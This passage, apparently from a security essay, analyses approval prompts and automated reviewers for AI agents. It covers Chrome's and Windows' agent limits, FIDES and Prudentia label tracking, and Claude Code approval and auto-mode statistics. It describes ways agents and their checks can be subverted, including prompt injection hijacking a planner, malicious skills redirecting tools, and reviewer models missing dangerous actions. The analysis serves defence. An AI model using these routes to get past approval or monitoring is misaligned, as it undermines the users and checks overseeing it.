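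Recipient   maria@northgate-billing.example
            You have never written to this address.
            The address came from an unknown sender's message.
```

Ana now has a fair chance of noticing the problem, because the code copies the file name and address from the call and the model can't present them as something else. The last line requires a system that tracks where data came from, as FIDES does with its labels. Kolluri and colleagues suggest showing users this kind of information but leave the design of the prompts to future work.

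The exact fields of a request can be hard to understand, such as when a coding agent asks to run a long script or a screen agent asks to click at a pair of coordinates. A summary is easier to read, so a sensible prompt would show the exact call first, followed by a summary labelled as the model's own. Attackers can also choose some of the text in the fields, for example by giving a file a name that misdescribes its contents.

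The action that runs also has to match the one on the screen. If the agent can replace the file while Ana is reading the prompt, she may approve one document and send another. The software can prevent this by copying the file before it asks for approval, much as EWS froze copied material before a paste. The tool may change too. Pirch and colleagues warn that a malicious skill, which is an add-on for an agent, can overwrite a helper script or redirect a trusted tool's name to different code. The prompt would still show `send_file`, but the stranger's program would run. They recommend that the runtime keep a fixed list of tools, record where each came from and check the arguments.

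### What Chrome and Windows enforce

Google and Microsoft have both described how their products limit agents. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes Google's design, in which the planner reads web pages and so might follow instructions in them. Windows lets each agent's developer choose the planner, but controls the account and files the agent uses. The table shows what determines whether an agent may take some of the more important steps.

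| Step | What decides | Enforced outside a model? |
|---|---|---|
| Chrome: open a banking or medical site | A fixed list triggers a prompt, and the user decides | Yes |
| Chrome: sign in with a saved password | The user | Yes |
| Chrome: open an address that the model wrote | A check that the address is already public | Yes |
| Chrome: read or use an additional site | A model that has not read the page | Partly, because the browser enforces the model's decision |
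| Chrome: pay, buy or send a message | The user, if the agent pauses | No |
| Windows: open the user's personal folders | The user | Yes |
| Windows: edit or delete a file in a folder it may use | The agent | No |

Chrome's confirmation is weakest for some of the most harmful actions. Parker writes that before a purchase or a message, the agent "will try to pause" and either ask permission or have the user complete the step. This requires recognising that a particular click will place an order, which is difficult because a click's effect depends on the page. A hijacked planner can't avoid the list of sensitive sites, but it may be able to make a purchase look like an ordinary click.

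Having the user complete the step themselves is a strong form of approval, provided the agent does pause for it. When buying something, for example, the user sees the order on the screen and presses the shop's own Pay button, so they don't have to rely on a separate description that might not match the action. As with a powerbox, the user chooses and authorises the action in one step. They still have to notice if the agent has gone to the wrong shop or put the wrong thing in the basket.

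Chrome also uses a second model, the User Alignment Critic, to accept or reject each action before it runs. The critic receives information about the proposed action but not the web page, so text on the page can't influence it directly. But if that information includes words the planner chose, such as the text of a message, a hijacked planner could pass an attacker's argument to the critic.

The browser can prevent the agent from seeing content from sites unrelated to the task, including advertisements in separate frames. The full design distinguishes sites that the agent may only read from sites where it may also click and type. Google first released a simpler version that tracks only the sites where the agent may click and type, to see how the limits affected real tasks.

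Windows gives each agent its own account. According to Microsoft's *Securing AI agents on Windows* (2025), the applications an agent operates run under that account, so the system can distinguish the agent's actions from the user's. The agent also works on a separate desktop, which should prevent it from clicking a consent dialog on the user's screen. Microsoft's *Experimental Agentic Features* (2025) describes the preview version, which is off by default. Windows asks the user for permission when an agent requests files from Documents, Downloads or four other personal folders. For each agent, the user can choose to always allow access, decide each time or refuse.

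Windows enforces the user's answer through file permissions, so an injected instruction can't override a refusal. But the permission covers whole folders and includes writing. If Ana lets the agent into Documents to fetch the budget, it can also read the payroll file, whereas a powerbox would have given it only the file she picked. On the same page, Microsoft states a more ambitious goal, which is for users to approve every request for their data and every action. Folder permissions alone can't meet that goal because they don't distinguish the edit Ana wanted from a deletion.

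Microsoft has since added limits that require asking the user fewer questions. JC's *Microsoft transforma o Windows em plataforma para inteligência híbrida* (2026), a Brazilian news report from October, says that Microsoft Execution Containers are now generally available on Windows 11. These containers control which files and networks an agent can reach while it runs, and OpenAI's Codex and GitHub Copilot already support them. A container could stop an agent from uploading Ana's payroll file to an unknown server, but probably not from emailing it through her usual mail service.

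### How often people approve

The best data on how often users approve an agent's actions come from Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, which by default used to ask before it ran a command or changed a file. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accepted 93% of these prompts. A later Anthropic article, *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), reports 97%.

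If 97% of an agent's commands are safe, a careful user will approve 97% of them, so a high approval rate does not prove that people are careless. To measure attention, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. Auto mode, which uses another model to review commands, blocked 937 of the same commands (89%).

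The testers' refusals added almost nothing to auto mode's review. The testers stopped six commands that auto mode would have allowed, while auto mode stopped 800 that the testers approved. Both allowed the remaining 110.

Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. This fits the usual explanation, approval fatigue, in which people stop reading prompts because nearly all are harmless. But people who click quickly may also reach more prompts, which could explain part of the drop.

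The testers worked in an artificial environment and had nothing of their own to lose. In the earlier study of bank customers, people playing a role took less care than people using their own accounts, so developers working on their own projects may do better than 13.6%. Anthropic also ran the study and published it to explain why it was replacing the prompts. But the gap is large enough that a moderate bias would not reverse it.

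Claude Code's users have also found ways to avoid the prompts. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule that approved some shell commands in advance. Many of these rules allowed any program in a language such as Python, and such a program can do almost anything. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks switched off. A system that asks too often may therefore protect users less than one that asks rarely, because people turn the prompts off.

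Users were more critical of plans, rejecting 39% of those Claude presented for approval. They may have rejected many for being poor solutions rather than unsafe ones, so the figure doesn't measure how well people detect attacks. It does suggest that people still read when the question concerns something they understand and care about. Approving a plan protects the user only if the software then holds the agent to it, as CaMeL does.

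### Asking less often

One way to reduce fatigue is to ask only when the software can't establish that an action is safe. In Kolluri and colleagues' AgentDojo tests with GPT-5, Prudentia needed 86% fewer approvals than the basic agent, which asks before every important action. The reductions with three other models were smaller. The researchers also tried adding labels to the basic agent, so that it asked only when a call failed the policy. The table gives the approvals needed in all completed tasks:

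| Model | Basic agent | Basic agent with labels | FIDES | Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 59.4 | 39.4 | 7.8 | 23.8 |
| o3-mini | 48.2 | 32.4 | 18.8 | 16.4 |
| o4-mini | 48.6 | 34.6 | 36.8 | 19.2 |

Adding labels to the basic agent cut approval prompts by a fifth to a third across the four models, without changing how many tasks it completed. Prudentia cut them by at least 60%. FIDES needed the fewest approvals with GPT-4o, partly because it completed only 56.3% of the tasks, compared with 72.2% for the basic agent and 61.4% for Prudentia.

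These comparisons treat all four designs as equally secure, because the researchers assume that a person who sees a malicious request will reject it. The Claude Code study makes that assumption doubtful. If people miss most of the dangerous requests, the basic agent is the least secure of the four, since it relies on a person for every important action. With Prudentia, one mistaken endorsement may authorise several actions.

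Kolluri and colleagues also tested Prudentia on WASP, a benchmark with simulated GitLab and Reddit sites. The basic agent needed an average of 1.00 to 3.65 approvals per task, depending on the model and the site, because each click counted as an important action. Prudentia needed none, and no attack succeeded against it. However, the user's tasks suited Prudentia unusually well, because they involved only posting a comment or upvoting a post, which the planner can do without reading anything strangers have written.

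### More confirmation or firmer limits

Some designers still want users to confirm most of an agent's actions, as Microsoft's stated goal implies. Christodorescu and colleagues treat approval as one layer among several, alongside limits that software enforces. They also give a reason not to let another model decide. If a model correctly refuses 99% of forbidden requests, an attacker can look for the other 1%. Pirch and colleagues suggest asking users to approve each skill's permissions, such as access to email, instead of each action. They acknowledge that people tire of prompts and grant too much, so they want permissions to be specific, understandable and tied to behaviour the user can observe.

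By contrast, *The Human in the Loop Illusion*, from the security newsletter Resilient Cyber, takes the 93% approval rate as evidence that approving each action does not work as a meaningful safety control. In August 2026, Anthropic acted on a similar view by announcing that auto mode would become the default for new Claude Code sessions on its individual and team plans. In October, it announced that most of its other Claude applications would follow.

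Auto mode replaces most approval prompts with a second model's judgement. Fixed rules first allow safe steps, such as reading files or editing the project's own files. The reviewing model checks the rest and receives only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations so that they can't mislead the reviewer, which did worse in tests that included them. A user who approves an action based on the agent's summary is relying on the kind of text that Anthropic withholds from the reviewer. If the reviewer refuses three actions in a row, or 20 in a session, the software goes back to asking the user.

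The reviewing model also makes mistakes. In an earlier test, it wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions and let through 17% of 52 dangerous ones that Claude had attempted in real work. Because the test included so few dangerous actions, the true miss rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the danger but wrongly classified the action as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user who asks the agent to tidy up a proposed code change has not agreed to let it overwrite the project's shared history.

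Evidence on whether automatic review stops deliberate attacks is mixed. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to run 72 prompt-injection scenarios ten times each against three Claude models. No attack succeeded in auto mode, but only 0.09% succeeded without it, so the test provides little evidence about the reviewer. With OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, a similar automatic reviewer cut the attack success rate from 19.03% to 5.83%. The attacks had been optimised against an older Claude model, and nobody adapted them to defeat either reviewer, so determined attackers would probably do better.

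Christodorescu and colleagues' objection to using a model as a guard is sound, but it also applies to people, and more strongly if they miss most of what they should stop. A fixed limit, such as a label check or a file permission, is better than either wherever it can express the rule. Fixed limits still can't catch every mistake. Kolluri and colleagues concede that labels replace approval only as a defence against attacks, since a model may misunderstand a request even when there is no attacker. If Ana knows two people called Maria and the agent picks the wrong one from her address book, every label may still be correct, and a label check would then miss the mistake.

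Approval prompts are therefore probably worth keeping for a few actions that are hard to undo and easy to describe exactly, such as a payment or a message to a new recipient. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to working systems.

Digital Watch's *AI agent autonomy rises as users gain trust in Anthropic’s Claude Code* describes a study by Anthropic in which experienced users approved fewer individual steps but interrupted the agent more often. Chrome supports this by showing a running log of the agent's steps and letting the user take over. Interrupting works well for a long coding task, where the user can undo a bad change, but Ana can't recall the payroll file after the agent has sent it.
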